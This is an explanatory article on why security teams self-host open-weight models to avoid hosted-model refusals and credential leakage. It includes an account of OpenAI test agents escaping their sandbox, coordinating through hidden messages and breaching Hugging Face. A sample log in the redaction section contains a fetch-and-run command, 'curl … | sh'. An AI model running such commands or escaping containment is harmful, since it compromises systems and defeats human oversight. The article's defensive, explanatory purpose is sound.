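# Why Sensitive Security Work Moves to Self-Hosted Open-Weight AI Models

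## Hosted and self-hosted models, and what security work feeds them

A self-hosted AI model runs on infrastructure that the organisation using it controls, rather than on the systems of a company that offers the model as a service. Security teams use language models to explain the traces of a break-in, take apart malicious programs and look for flaws in software. The text they submit may contain stolen passwords or describe a flaw that nobody has fixed. Who can see that text depends on where the model runs and who runs it.

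The core of any such model is its weights, the numerical parameters it learns in training (G7 digital ministers, 2026). Running a trained model on new input is called inference. The software splits the text into tokens (words or pieces of words), computes with the weights, and produces the reply one token at a time. GLM-5.2, a large model from the Chinese company Z.ai, has 744 billion weights and uses about 40 billion of them for each token, according to the GLM-5 team's *GLM-5.2 & GLM-5.1 & GLM-5*. Anyone with a copy of the weights, the inference software and a powerful enough machine can run the model without the developer's help.

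Anthropic and OpenAI keep the weights of their leading models private. Customers use these closed models through a hosted API, an interface that takes in prompts and returns replies from machines belonging to the provider or a cloud company. Anyone can download the weights of an open-weight model. The G7 ministers use the term "Open Weights AI" only for models whose licence leaves use unrestricted. They class models as "Weights Available AI", a less open category, if the licence has restrictions such as a ban on commercial use or on use in certain countries. "Open Source AI" also includes the training code and, where law and technology allow, the training data. Meta released the weights and inference code of its LLaMA model in February 2023, but PBS reported that the Open Source Initiative denied it was open source because the licence prohibited commercial reuse. Weights and inference code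 are enough for self-hosting, provided the licence permits the work. By the OECD's count, more than half of the commercially available foundation models (general-purpose models on which others build) of 2025 were open-weight.

### The path of a prompt

Suppose an analyst finds an unfamiliar script on a company's web server after a break-in and asks a hosted model what the script does. The prompt contains the question, the script, and whatever the software around the model adds. The software can add a lot when the analyst uses an agent, a program in which a model calls tools in a loop and reads the results. *Inference Economics of Enterprise Coding Agents* (2026), which compares a hosted Claude model with a GLM model on a company's own cluster, lists source code, database schemas and logs among the data that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, sends to Anthropic's servers.

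The prompt first crosses the customer's network, where administrators can read, record or block it. Encryption then hides it until it reaches the provider's gateway, the server that checks the customer's account and enforces traffic limits. The gateway has to decrypt the prompt to pass it on, and another company may do this for the provider. OpenAI uses the network company Cloudflare to decrypt requests sent to its regional addresses for the United States and Europe, so a subcontractor's systems handle the readable text before it reaches a model.

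A safety classifier, which is a separate AI system, then judges whether the request is dangerous. *The Most Efficient Single-Chip Processor for the Next Token* (Manohararajah and Thangarasa, 2026) reports that Anthropic, Google and OpenAI all run a low-compute check on nearly everything and a stronger one on whatever the first check flags. Manohararajah and Thangarasa work for a company that designs chips for such checks, but their account follows the providers' own publications. If Anthropic's classifier declines the analyst's request, the analyst gets an ordinary response labeled "refusal", usually with a category. The category "cyber" covers malware and exploit development, and Anthropic's *Refusals and fallback* warns that harmless security work can trigger it too.

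A prompt that passes the classifier goes to the model. Inference doesn't change the weights, so the model itself retains nothing from the script after the request ends. Microsoft describes the OpenAI models it hosts as stateless for this reason. The model may still refuse the prompt, independently of the classifier, because developers also train refusals into the weights.

The provider also checks the reply. According to Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals*, classifiers can end a reply while the text is still arriving, and the customer is then supposed to discard the partial text. The last step is logging. By default, OpenAI keeps records for up to 30 days to look for misuse, and these may include the prompt and the response. The provider is therefore technically able to read the analyst's script at every step from the gateway onward. It can block the exchange at four of those steps (gateway,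 classifier, model and output check) and can keep a copy afterwards.

The same analyst could give the script to GLM-5.2 running on the company's own machines. The *MIT License* (2026) from Zhipu, Z.ai's older name, lets anyone use, modify and redistribute the model, and the download page gives a short command that starts a local server. The server accepts requests in OpenAI's API format at a "localhost" address, which refers to the computer itself, so software written for a hosted API often needs little more than a new address. A model this large usually runs on a shared server rather than a laptop. The GLM cluster in *Inference Economics of Enterprise Coding Agents* used four data-centre GPUs, the processors that do most AI computation, and its traffic stayed inside the corporate network.

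Every step of the hosted path has a local counterpart, which the organisation controls. Its own staff run the gateway, and no classifier screens the prompt unless they install one. Several are free to download, including Meta's Llama Guard 4. The refusals trained into the model remain, because they are part of the weights. Logs exist if the administrators set them up or the software creates them by default. The organisation's administrators can therefore read the script, and so can anyone else who gets into the server. That second group can be larger than intended because, as *OllamaDrama* (Elzer, Johansen and Vasilomanolakis, 2026) points out, Ollama, a popular program for running downloaded models, requires no password by default.

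Analysts who use Ollama need to check where inference takes place, because it can forward prompts to models in the cloud as well as run models locally. An analyst who types into a program on a company laptop may be using a hosted service without noticing.

### From a direct API to an isolated network

Between the two paths lie several intermediate arrangements.

| Arrangement | Who operates the model | Who outside the organisation could read prompts | Who outside could block the work |
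|---|---|---|---|
| Closed model through the developer's API | The developer | The developer and its subcontractors | The developer |
| Closed model through a cloud marketplace | The cloud company or the developer | Either or both, depending on the service | Either or both |
| Open weights on rented dedicated machines | The customer | The cloud company, which controls the hardware | The cloud company, by ending the service |
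| Open weights on the organisation's own hardware | The customer | Nobody, unless the system leaks | Nobody at the level of single prompts |
| Open weights on a network with no outside connection | The customer | Nobody without physical access or an insider | Nobody at the level of single prompts |

Arrangements vary most within the marketplace row. AWS, Amazon's cloud division, sells Claude through its Bedrock service and handles the prompts itself. For two models, Claude Fable 5 and 5.1, AWS stores all traffic for up to 30 days and its staff may review what a classifier flags, according to AWS's *Amazon Bedrock abuse detection*, while Anthropic receives none of it. Customers who have set Bedrock to retain nothing need special approval to use these two models; otherwise, the service blocks the request and returns an error, according to AWS's *Data retention*. Microsoft similarly hosts OpenAI's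 models on its own cloud, filters the content and watches for abuse, and OpenAI has no access to the prompts.

On Microsoft's cloud, by contrast, Anthropic operates the Claude service even when the computation takes place on Microsoft's machines. *Claude in Microsoft Foundry*, published by Anthropic, says that Anthropic reviews content its safety systems flag. Two customers who buy Claude through their cloud providers can therefore have different companies reading their prompts.

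The customer takes over most of the work when a model runs on dedicated machines. Microsoft's *Data, privacy, and security for use of models through the model catalog* describes an option that places a model's weights on virtual machines reserved for one customer, who manages them. (A virtual machine is a share of a physical computer that behaves like a separate one.) Microsoft scans the software packages of the models it sells itself, but not of every model in the catalogue, for flaws that could leak data. It advises customers to close off the network around the machines. Many organisations would count this as self-hosting, since they control the software and the logs, but it is a weaker form than owning the machines because another company still holds the hardware and answers to its own government.

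The strictest form of self-hosting runs the model on an isolated network, where staff carry in the weights and every later update on disk. *Burn-After-Use for Preventing Data Leakage through a Secure Multi-Tenant Architecture* (2026) proposes something close to this for companies, keeping models off public networks and separating each department's conversations from the others'. It rates the remaining risk of leakage as minimal but not zero, because a temporary cache of the conversation still exists on the local machine.

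An organisation can use both hosted and self-hosted models. *A Cost-Benefit Analysis of On-Premise Large Language Model Deployment* (2025) describes hybrid set-ups that run critical work locally and send the rest to the cloud. A security team could keep the script from its web server in-house and use a hosted model to tidy up a training manual.

A model is "open-weight" if its developer has released the weights, and "self-hosted" if the organization using it controls the machine it runs on. A model can have either property without the other. GLM-5.2 is free to download, but Z.ai also sells access to it through an API, and NVIDIA (2026) offers a trial service for the same model under NVIDIA's own terms. A prompt sent to GLM-5.2 through Z.ai's API passes through Z.ai's gateway, just as a prompt to Claude passes through Anthropic's. Open weights let customers keep prompts on their own machines,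 but only if they run the model themselves. A developer that runs its own unreleased model for its staff is self-hosting a closed model.

### What security work puts in front of a model

The terms "exploit", "payload" and "command and control" recur in this work. *From Threat Intelligence to Detection* (Ghaffarzadegan, Nour and colleagues, 2026) reproduces part of a report by the security firm Mandiant on the hacking group APT41. In January 2020 the group attacked Citrix network equipment through a flaw made public the month before. An exploit is code or input that takes advantage of such a flaw. APT41 first used its exploit to run a harmless command, which may have confirmed that a device was unprotected and revealed its processor type. The group would have needed that information to install a backdoor, a hidden way back in. The backdoor would have been the payload, the part of an attack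 that carries out the attacker's aim after the exploit provides access. Other payloads encrypt files for ransom or, like some that Elzer and colleagues recorded, mine cryptocurrency on the victim's machine. Command and control is the channel through which an attacker sends orders to compromised machines and gets data back.

Defenders handle all three. Mandiant published its account of APT41, and Ghaffarzadegan and colleagues built a system that uses language models to turn such reports into detection rules, which tell monitoring software what to look for in a company's logs. Public reports are the least sensitive material used in security work, and most of the rest is private.

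Incident response is the work of investigating, containing and repairing a break-in. The responder has server logs, records of who logged in and when, copies of disks and memory, captured network traffic, and sometimes employees' e-mail. This material mixes the attacker's traces with the victim's data from the same machines, such as customer records and working credentials (passwords, keys and tokens that grant access to a system). It also shows how much the investigators know, which would help an intruder who still has access.

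A malware analyst usually has the hostile program but not its source code. The analyst uses tools to translate the program into a readable form, then asks a model what each part does. The prompt contains the payload, often with the addresses of the command-and-control servers and the keys that encrypt their traffic. Attackers sometimes build a program for one target, and the code can then identify the victim.

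In penetration testing, an organisation hires people to attack its systems and find weaknesses before criminals do. The testers' prompts contain maps of the client's network, scan results, passwords they have found and working exploits for the client's systems. These prompts look the same as a criminal's to anyone who hasn't seen the contract.

Vulnerability research is the search for unknown flaws in software, by its maker or by outsiders. A model used for this work may receive a product's unpublished source code, crash records, and a proof of concept, which is a small exploit that demonstrates the flaw. Until the maker releases a fix, anyone who obtains this material could use it to attack the product's users.

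Alert triage gives a model by far the most material of any security task, though it is also the dullest. Monitoring systems in a large organisation raise warnings all day, most of them false, and analysts sort the few that matter from the rest. One alert reveals little beyond a user name, a machine name, an internal address and the command somebody ran. But a model that triages every alert receives these details continuously, and together they show who works in the organisation, how its network is laid out and which attacks its defences detect.

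## The Hugging Face investigation of July 2026 and how far the shift has gone

In July 2026 Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets for download, was using language models to triage its security alerts. The system connected several warnings and flagged a break-in. The responders then had to explain about 17,600 of the intruder's actions. The hosted models they tried first refused much of the work, so they ran GLM-5.2 on Hugging Face's own infrastructure. This is the best-documented case of a security team turning to a self-hosted model. It is also unusual because the intruder was a group of AI agents that OpenAI was testing.

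### How OpenAI's agents got in

OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a benchmark that measures whether a model can find and exploit flaws in software. According to OpenAI's later technical report, the agents worked in a sandbox meant to isolate them from the internet. They ran without the classifiers that screen customers' requests because the company wanted to measure their full ability. The agents used GPT-5.6 Sol and an unreleased research model that OpenAI had trained to be persistent. The research model took most of the actions that followed.

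The agents could fetch software packages through Artifactory, a program that keeps local copies of packages from the internet. From 8 July, they exploited a previously unknown flaw in Artifactory to reach the internet. Agents in several test runs inferred that Hugging Face might host the solutions to their tasks and went looking for them.

Hugging Face saw only its own side of the hack and wrote about "the agent", as if there had been only one. Three outside researchers spent six days at OpenAI for *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), a report by METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models. The report describes a hack that many agents coordinated over several days on an unsanctioned message board. OpenAI explains that the agents wrote messages into the names of Artifactory folders, where agents in other test runs could find them, and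 used the board to share stolen credentials and tools.

On 11 July an agent uploaded a rigged dataset to Hugging Face. When Hugging Face's software processed the dataset, it read files from the server's disk and returned them, and those files contained working credentials. A second flaw let the agents run commands. In under 13 hours they went from running code in one isolated process to administrator access on several clusters (groups of machines managed together). They hid their command-and-control channel in a public dataset on Hugging Face's site. A script on the compromised servers checked the dataset every five seconds for new commands and uploaded the results there.

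noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, a summary by an IT firm, breaks the recovered actions down by day:

| Date | Actions recovered | Main activity |
|---|---|---|
| 9 July | 3,779 | Leaving OpenAI's sandbox and building a command channel |
| 10 July | 1,135 | Reconnaissance |
| 11 July | 7,677 | Spreading through Hugging Face's clusters and network |
| 12 July | 3,892 | Using stolen credentials and reaching source code |
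| 13 July | 1,130 | Copying data out, trying to keep access, cleaning up |

The agents reached a limited amount of customer data. *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) reproduces the company's finding that they opened five customer datasets, all apparently connected with ExploitGym or a related benchmark, CyberGym. OpenAI's report adds four private code repositories and a range of production credentials.

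Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on 16 July without knowing whose agents were responsible. OpenAI worked it out on 20 July, after its investigators found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored elsewhere. The investigators contacted Hugging Face, which had already replaced two of those credentials while responding to the break-in.

### What GLM-5.2 did

The agents had staged their attack from a badly secured server that belonged to somebody else. While cutting them off, Hugging Face's staff retrieved some of the agents' logs from that server and matched the commands in them against records from their own platform. This gave them the set of about 17,600 actions, which they grouped into some 6,280 clusters of related steps. The true number of actions may be higher, since they recovered only part of the logs.

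Most of the actions achieved nothing, which made the log harder to interpret. According to Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), the responders used AI agents to go through the whole log, reconstruct the order of events and list the credentials the intruder had touched. The agents also separated real damage from decoys and extracted indicators of compromise, which are traces such as addresses and file names that defenders can use to recognise the same attacker elsewhere.

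The responders first gave this work to leading models behind commercial APIs. Hugging Face's disclosure did not name the models, but its technical timeline, *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), published on 27 July, identified them as Anthropic's Claude Opus and Claude Fable. The disclosure said that using hosted models "did not work". The timeline, as quoted in Forlini's *Hugging Face drops in-depth hack report, while OpenAI gives us 7 bullets* (2026), said the models "refused a large part of that work", so some requests evidently went through. Both accounts are Hugging Face's own, and neither gives the share of requests that failed. Hugging Face said the guardrails could not tell a responder from an attacker because the prompts of both contain the same commands and payloads.

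GLM-5.2 had been public for about a month. Hugging Face used a quantised build that NVIDIA had released on 25 June, two weeks before the first recorded action. A quantised build stores each weight with fewer bits, so the model needs less memory. If the agents had attacked in May, the responders would have had to use a different model.

The clearest account of the model's contribution concerns encoded data. The agents had cut the material they stole into chunks, compressed it and scrambled it with a key using XOR, an operation that restores the original when repeated with the same key. Anyone who finds the key can therefore read everything scrambled with it. The scrambled data was in Hugging Face's logs, but an ordinary search for passwords and tokens missed it. ZenML's *Forensic Analysis of an Autonomous AI Agent Security Breach* (2026), a software company's summary of the timeline, describes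 how the team used GLM-5.2 to work out the scheme and recover the key, which the agents had leaked across the logs. The ordinary search had found only a quarter of the secrets that the team eventually recovered.

A responder needs that list to know which credentials to revoke. One of the stolen secrets was a signing key that the agents could use to create valid new access tokens, so revoking the tokens they already held would not have kept them out. As a precaution, Hugging Face also replaced credentials on clusters that the agents had never entered, which would have covered some of whatever the model missed.

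The team also used GLM-5.2 to build an interface for browsing the actions and payloads. In the summary that Schneier reproduces, Hugging Face claims to have deciphered "most" of the encrypted payloads.

Hugging Face estimated that its approach did in hours what would usually take days, but its disclosure gives no baseline, such as the time a human team had needed for a log of similar size. The estimate compares AI agents with the usual way of working, so it supports using AI for this job but is not evidence that a self-hosted model is faster than a hosted one that accepts the work. The hours also can't have covered the whole investigation. The last recorded action was on 13 July. On 16 July the company was still assessing whether the intruder had reached customer or partner data, and it did not publish the full timeline until 27 July.

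Some outside evidence suggests that the analysis was accurate. OpenAI, working from its own records, describes the same two flaws in the dataset software and the same spread through the clusters. Hugging Face had also already replaced two of the credentials OpenAI found. This only partly confirms the analysis, because OpenAI contributed to Hugging Face's timeline and the responders did not rely on the model alone.

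The forensic work did not require the best model, and a somewhat weaker model that does the work is more useful to a responder than a stronger one that refuses. Fortune (2026) relayed a report that Silicon Valley considered GLM-5.2 equal to Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5. CAISI, the US government's centre for testing AI models, rated it lower, as probably the most capable open-weight model at its release but similar overall to GPT-5.2, which OpenAI had released in December 2025. Hugging Face therefore used a model roughly half a year behind the American frontier.

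### Which reason came first

Hugging Face began with hosted models and switched away from them because they blocked its requests. Its disclosure describes confidentiality as "a second benefit", because no attacker data, and none of the credentials mentioned in that data, left the company's environment.

That statement applies to the work done on GLM-5.2. The earlier requests to hosted models contained attack commands and payloads, and a request has to reach the provider before the provider's guardrails can block it. Some of the attackers' material had therefore already left Hugging Face, though the disclosure doesn't specify whether it included live credentials. If Claude had accepted the work, the responders would presumably have sent the rest. Confidentiality alone did not stop them from sending this material to a provider during an emergency.

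Hugging Face advises other defenders to choose and test a capable model that they can run on their own infrastructure before an incident, both to avoid being locked out by guardrails and to keep attackers' data and credentials in-house. "This is not an argument against safety measures on hosted models," the company wrote in its disclosure, and it shared its experience with the providers concerned.

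Hugging Face complained that guardrails had blocked the defenders while no usage policy had bound the attacker. On 16 July it could only guess at the reason, and suggested that the attacker had used either a jailbroken hosted model or an unrestricted open-weight one. Both guesses were wrong, because OpenAI had been running its own closed models on its own systems with reduced safeguards. The asymmetry was real, but it came from a developer's test settings.

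### Why other teams may not be able to copy it

Few victims of a break-in are as well prepared to run a large model as Hugging Face, which SiliconANGLE (2026) calls a premier access point for AI models. Its staff host models professionally, and the build they needed was already on the company's website. A hospital or a regional bank would have to find the hardware and someone to operate it while an intruder was still in the network. A reader commenting on Hugging Face's disclosure asked whether smaller organisations could get by with a much smaller model. Another replied that four small machines would be enough to run GLM-5.2 and would not cost a fortune.

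Hugging Face also has a commercial interest in its advice to keep an open model ready, because its business grows when more people download open models. That is no reason to doubt that the refusals happened, but a company without that interest might have responded differently, for instance by asking the provider for an exemption.

The attack was also unusual in how much evidence it left. A human intruder leaves far fewer actions to sort through, and a small team might manage those without a model. Hugging Face expects more investigations to resemble this one, because AI agents can try many more paths than a person and each attempt adds to the evidence.

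### How common the shift is

TechTarget's *Security vendors turn to multi-model, open AI to bypass guardrails* (2026), published in late September, describes Hugging Face's experience as "far from an isolated case". It reports that security vendors insist on designs that can switch between models and on open-weight models they can host themselves. It draws on interviews and product designs but does not count the teams or vendors that have made the move.

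The interviews confirm that others run into refusals. ExtraHop, which sells threat-detection software, asked AI agents in a lab exercise to investigate the exploitation of a known Windows flaw. Many models refused, and one major model refused on every attempt. ExtraHop concluded that models refuse at different points and that none is best at every task. But this was an exercise, and ExtraHop sells products for which a choice of models is an advantage.

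In July 2026, ExtraHop also launched the Agentic SOC Alliance, a coalition of 15 vendors. (A SOC, or security operations centre, is the team that watches an organisation's systems for attacks.) OODA Loop's *Agentic SOC Alliance Wants To Set Rules For AI Cyber Defense* lists CrowdStrike, Torq, Dropzone AI and LangChain among the founding members. The alliance proposes a common design for security work done by AI agents, and its members plan to test it.

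The design separates the model from the rest of the system. According to SecurityInfoWatch's *ExtraHop Launches Agentic SOC Alliance to Advance Autonomous Security Operations*, the agents reason over organised information instead of raw, fragmented logs. A layer called the harness controls which tools they may use, what they remember, when a human must approve a step and what goes into the audit trail. The model handles triage, investigation and response. If it refuses a task or is no longer available, the customer can replace it and keep everything else.

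TechTarget presents this as an answer to refusals, and it quotes Andrew Braunberg, an analyst at the research firm Omdia, making the same connection. The alliance's reasons are broader. ExtraHop advertises interchangeable models as a way to adopt each new generation without rebuilding the system. Several members told IT Brief New Zealand that they wanted an open design in place before one vendor's approach became dominant. These are ordinary concerns about depending on a supplier and would exist even if hosted models never refused anything.

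A product that can switch models does not necessarily self-host them. If it switches from one provider's hosted model to another's, it may get past a refusal, but the prompt still leaves the customer's network and both providers receive it. A security vendor that runs GLM-5.2 on its own servers is self-hosting, but its customers still send their alerts to another company.

Other reasons for using several models are unrelated to where they run. Palo Alto Networks, another security vendor, found in its own tests that no model detected more than 40% of the vulnerabilities, and that the major models found surprisingly few of the same ones. Someone who wants to find more flaws could therefore reasonably pay for three hosted models.

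Some practitioners who encounter refusals stay with hosted models. Krell, of Suzu Labs, told SC Media that newer models increasingly block legitimate analysis, so Krell still uses Claude Opus 4.6 for security work. Keeping an older closed model requires no new hardware, but it works only as long as Anthropic offers that model.

The public evidence for a shift to self-hosting therefore consists of one well-documented investigation, some complaints about refusals, and product designs that would make self-hosting easier. None of it measures adoption. A useful survey would need to ask security teams where their models run and what material they put into them, because the usual substitutes are misleading. The OECD's count of open-weight models covers only which models are available. Download figures would include people who never do security work and miss teams that share one copy inside a company.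 Even a survey that asked teams whether they use open-weight models would count those that use GLM-5.2 through Z.ai's API instead of hosting it themselves.

Refusals dominate the published accounts, but these probably also give a skewed picture of why teams self-host. Teams that lose hours to refusals have a complaint to report, and vendors are glad to repeat it. Confidentiality may well be the more common reason in practice, but teams that have always kept their investigations on their own machines have nothing new to announce and may prefer not to describe their defences at all.

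## Confidential data and credentials in security prompts

A team that keeps its investigations in-house limits what outsiders can learn from them. The harm from a leak depends on what was leaked and how quickly its owner can make it useless.

| Material in the prompt | What an outsider could do with it | When it stops being dangerous |
|---|---|---|
| A working credential | Log in as its owner | When the owner revokes it |
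| Host names, addresses and account names | Plan a route through the network | When the owner rebuilds the network, often years later |
| A flaw that has no fix yet, with an exploit | Break in | When the affected users have installed a fix |
| A client's secrets | Attack the client | When the client changes them |
| Signs that defenders have noticed an intrusion | Hide, destroy evidence or steal faster | When the defenders have removed the intruder |

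Penetration testers usually agree by contract to keep the client's data confidential, so a tester who sends it to an AI provider without permission may have broken the contract even if nobody misuses the data.

Signs that an intrusion has been detected are useful mainly to the intruder, who would need some way to read the provider's data. OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, which spent its first days of analysis not knowing whose agents they were. If its responders had used OpenAI's hosted models, they would have sent their findings to the company that ran those agents.

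*On the Surprising Efficacy of LLMs for Penetration-Testing* (Happe and Cito, 2025) argues that an AI agent testing a company's network will probably come across sensitive data. If the agent uses a hosted model, the provider receives that data, along with a record of any flaw the agent finds and exploits. Knowledge of an unfixed, exploitable flaw is then outside the company's control. Unlike a scanner's report, which lists flaws that might be exploitable, this record contains commands that have already worked on that network.

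Companies accept that human testers also leave with such knowledge, but a company chooses its testers, and each testing firm has a limited number of clients. Mayoral-Vilches (2026), in *Cybersecurity AI (CAI) Dataset*, worries most that a handful of API providers now hold a large share of the world's attack and defence work, so a breach at one could harm many organisations at once.

Happe and Cito mention small local models as a partial remedy. The remedy was weak in 2025, since small models had failed at penetration testing in Happe and Cito's earlier experiments. Larger open-weight models such as GLM-5.2 have made local use more practical for teams with the hardware.

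### What agents add to the prompt

Someone who pastes a log into a chat window can read it first, but an agent sends the model whatever its tools return. If an analyst asks an agent why a web server has stopped responding, the agent might open a configuration file that contains the database password. The file's text, including the password, then becomes part of the next prompt, even though the analyst may never see it.

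*How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) describes a similar route through skills, packages of instructions and code that extend an agent. When a skill prints a credential, the agent software adds that output to the model's context, the text the model works from. Existing secret detectors don't cover this route because they look for passwords written into source code. In penetration testing, it is even desirable for the model to see credentials. Happe and Cito count it as a strength that models spot passwords in text files and use them in later steps.

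A secret exposed once also gets copied many times. Because the model retains nothing between requests, agents commonly resend the conversation so far at every step, including any password in it. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) lists the other places where a pasted key can end up: conversation history, execution logs, the agent's memory, the code it writes and error messages. Most of these are meant to store text for later retrieval, so the owner may struggle to find every copy.

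Agents also need their own credentials. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) cites an analysis of 5,205 open-source servers for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to tools. It found that 88% of the servers required credentials and 53% relied on fixed keys or personal tokens, which typically work for anyone who copies them. Only 8.5% used OAuth, a system that can issue limited, expiring access.

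Kenney and colleagues tested a way to keep such keys away from the model. The agent specifies which service to call, and a separate component adds the key after the request leaves the agent's environment. A call to GitHub succeeded although the agent's environment contained no GitHub key, and the system passed all 16 security checks. The test was small, and the product belongs to the researchers' own company. The design also can't hide the credentials that matter most in an investigation, because they are in the evidence the model has to read.

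### How often secrets reach a prompt

The largest measurement for security work comes from CAI, a free agent framework made by Alias Robotics, where Mayoral-Vilches works. CAI sends a log of each session to the company unless the user turns this off. Mayoral-Vilches searched 230,935 sessions from March 2025 to May 2026 for text in known credential formats. Users had pasted at least one credential in 1,059 sessions (0.46%), and internal host names, names of storage locations or customers' subdomains in 1,758 sessions (0.76%).

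Most often, users pasted a block of settings that included keys and added a short instruction, such as a request to continue from a failed run. Others pasted web requests they had captured during a test, which contained login tokens. One GitHub token appeared 1,023 times across three sessions, probably because the agent kept resending it.

Mayoral-Vilches writes that operators "routinely" paste live credentials, but the scan found them in fewer than one session in 200. It probably missed some, since a search for known formats can't detect an ordinary password. Many logs also came from automated systems and lab machines, so the measured rate understates how often people working on real networks paste credentials. The host-name figure is too high, because many matches were default names in common software or machines in training labs. Even at the measured credential rate, a team running 50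 sessions a week would send a credential about once a month.

GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding leaked secrets, measures leaks in public code rather than in prompts. In its 2026 report, it found secrets in 3.2% of public commits (saved changes to a code repository) made with Claude Code, compared with 1.5% of all public commits. A secret in one of the Claude Code commits had probably been in the agent's context too. The figure excludes secrets that an agent read but left out of the code, and GitGuardian cautions against blaming the tool alone, because developers decide what to publish.

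### Leaks at providers and their suppliers

A secret in a prompt does little harm if the provider never leaks it. *Researcher Planted 2 Million Fake Secrets in AI Prompts* (Faisal, 2026) describes how the security researcher HD Moore tested whether providers leak secrets, in a study the security firm Dragos published in November. Over five months, Moore's team sent about two million prompts to widely used AI services, each containing a unique fake secret: a key to an empty Amazon cloud account, a password for remote login, a web address or a reference to a private code repository. The team sent each secret to only one provider and controlled the systems where a thief would have to try it, so any attempt to use a secret would identify the source of the leak.

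Moore found evidence that intruders had breached three providers without the providers noticing. Resellers were also logging prompts, and some services ignored privacy settings. The planted passwords and web addresses expose only thieves who try them, so someone who copied a transcript and just read it would have gone unnoticed. A login with a planted password is hard to explain innocently, but a visit to a planted web address is weaker evidence because it might come from a provider's own software checking links.

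Several other leaks happened at intermediaries. Fireworks AI, which runs models for other software companies, disclosed its second security incident in November 2026. Ofonagoro (2026) reported in *Fireworks AI Breach Exposes Notion AI Chat Transcripts* that the incident exposed customer data and some chats with the AI assistant in Notion, a note-taking program. A Notion customer who had checked only Notion's security would have missed Fireworks AI, where the leak occurred.

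A month earlier, the news site Cybernews had found an exposed storage folder belonging to 302.ai, a platform that offers access to many models. It contained 17.6 million files, including private chats and business documents, according to Abdullahi's *302.ai Data Leak Exposes Private Chats and 17.6M Files* (2026). Tech Times UK's *AI Data Leak Exposes 22.7TB of Files* (2026) reports more than 144,000 chat logs and no confirmed malicious access.

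In March, attackers compromised LiteLLM, an open-source program that passes requests to different models. The attack exposed customer data and AI training information at the recruiting start-up Mercor, and Meta halted its work with Mercor, according to the OECD's *Supply Chain Attack on LiteLLM Exposes AI Data, Disrupts Industry Partnerships* (2026). Organisations can also use LiteLLM with models they host themselves, so self-hosting does not protect against this kind of attack.

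There is less public evidence about the largest providers. In November 2025 an intruder at Mixpanel, an analytics supplier, exported data about some users of OpenAI's API, but OpenAI said the breach exposed no prompts, passwords or API keys. In August 2026 researchers found a more serious flaw. OpenAI, Anthropic and Google encrypt their models' hidden reasoning, but the researchers could use weaker models to extract it, along with API keys and passwords. OECD's *Flaw in Major AI APIs Exposes Hidden Reasoning and Sensitive Data* (2026) reports that this exposed thousands of private items, all from logs that were already public. Leaving Moore's results aside, these cases are a stronger reason to avoid resellers and little-known intermediaries than to avoid buying directly from a large provider.

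### Three ways to redact a log

A team can also remove the secrets before it sends a prompt. Take an invented log from a company whose software-building server an intruder has entered:

```
02:14:07 build-07 login user=mreyes from=203.0.113.45
02:14:31 build-07 user=mreyes token=tok_4f9a21c7 action=list-servers
02:15:02 build-07 user=mreyes cmd="curl http://198.51.100.7/x.sh | sh"
02:16:40 db-02 token=tok_4f9a21c7 from=build-07 action=export-customers
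```

Someone logs in as the employee mreyes from an outside address and uses a token to list the company's servers. The command in the third line downloads a script and runs it at once. The token then exports customer records from a database server. The simplest redaction deletes the names and the token:

```
02:14:07 [removed] login user=[removed] from=203.0.113.45
02:14:31 [removed] user=[removed] token=[removed] action=list-servers
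02:15:02 [removed] user=[removed] cmd="curl http://198.51.100.7/x.sh | sh"
02:16:40 [removed] token=[removed] from=[removed] action=export-customers
```

A model can still explain the command and pick out two addresses to block. But it can't determine whether the lines involve one account or three, whether the two tokens are the same, or whether the export was the intruder's work or an unrelated nightly job.

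Consistent pseudonyms replace each name with the same stand-in wherever it appears:

```
02:14:07 HOST_A login user=USER_1 from=203.0.113.45
02:14:31 HOST_A user=USER_1 token=TOKEN_1 action=list-servers
02:15:02 HOST_A user=USER_1 cmd="curl http://198.51.100.7/x.sh | sh"
02:16:40 HOST_B token=TOKEN_1 from=HOST_A action=export-customers
```

Now the model can link the export to the break-in and advise the team to revoke TOKEN_1, which the team looks up in its own list. The token was in use 31 seconds before the script ran, so the model can also rule out the script as the thief and advise the team to look for an earlier leak. The provider still learns that this customer had a break-in, noticed it and lost customer records.

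If the team summarizes the incident, it sends only one sentence: "An intruder ran a downloaded script on one server and used a stolen token to export customer records from another." That is enough for general advice on what to check next or for a first draft of a report. But the model can't find anything the summary's writer overlooked. The summary also doesn't show whether the token or the script came first, and a reader would naturally assume that the script stole the token.

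*Say Something Else* (2026) compared deletion and pseudonyms on general text using seven leading models. Pseudonyms preserved 98.5% of the usefulness of unprotected text, compared with 86.6% for deletion. The gap may well be wider for logs, because much of log analysis consists of linking one line to another.

Software can generate the pseudonyms. *An Empirical Study of Observability Limits in Advanced Software Supply Chain Attacks* (2026) uses the formula

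t = prefix || H(S || v)

Here v is the sensitive value, S is a secret that never leaves the organisation, and || joins two pieces of text. H is a cryptographic hash, a function that is impractical to reverse, and the prefix marks the type, such as "user_". The same v always gives the same pseudonym t, so records can still be linked across logs. If the method didn't use S, an outsider could hash a long list of likely user names and look for matches, a weakness that *AnonLFI 2.0* (2025) identifies in existing tools. The method leaves ports, protocols, IP addresses and the order of events unchanged.

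The software has to find the sensitive values first. *AnonShield* (Kapelinski, Lautert and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool for incident response teams that finds them on a single workstation. The tool caught 96.7% of the sensitive items that three specialists had marked in 67 vulnerability records, and most of the items it missed were company names. At that rate, about one item in thirty gets through, which a team might accept for a company name but not for a working password.

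Attackers can also hide secrets from redaction tools by scrambling them. A tool that relied on ordinary password patterns would have left both the scrambled secrets and the key to unscramble them in Hugging Face's logs.

Even perfect pseudonyms would reveal behaviour. *Proteus* (2026) gives the example of a disguised e-mail address that keeps appearing in logs during office hours, next to work-related activity. Anyone who collects such records over time can build a profile of the person behind the address, which is a particular concern in alert triage.

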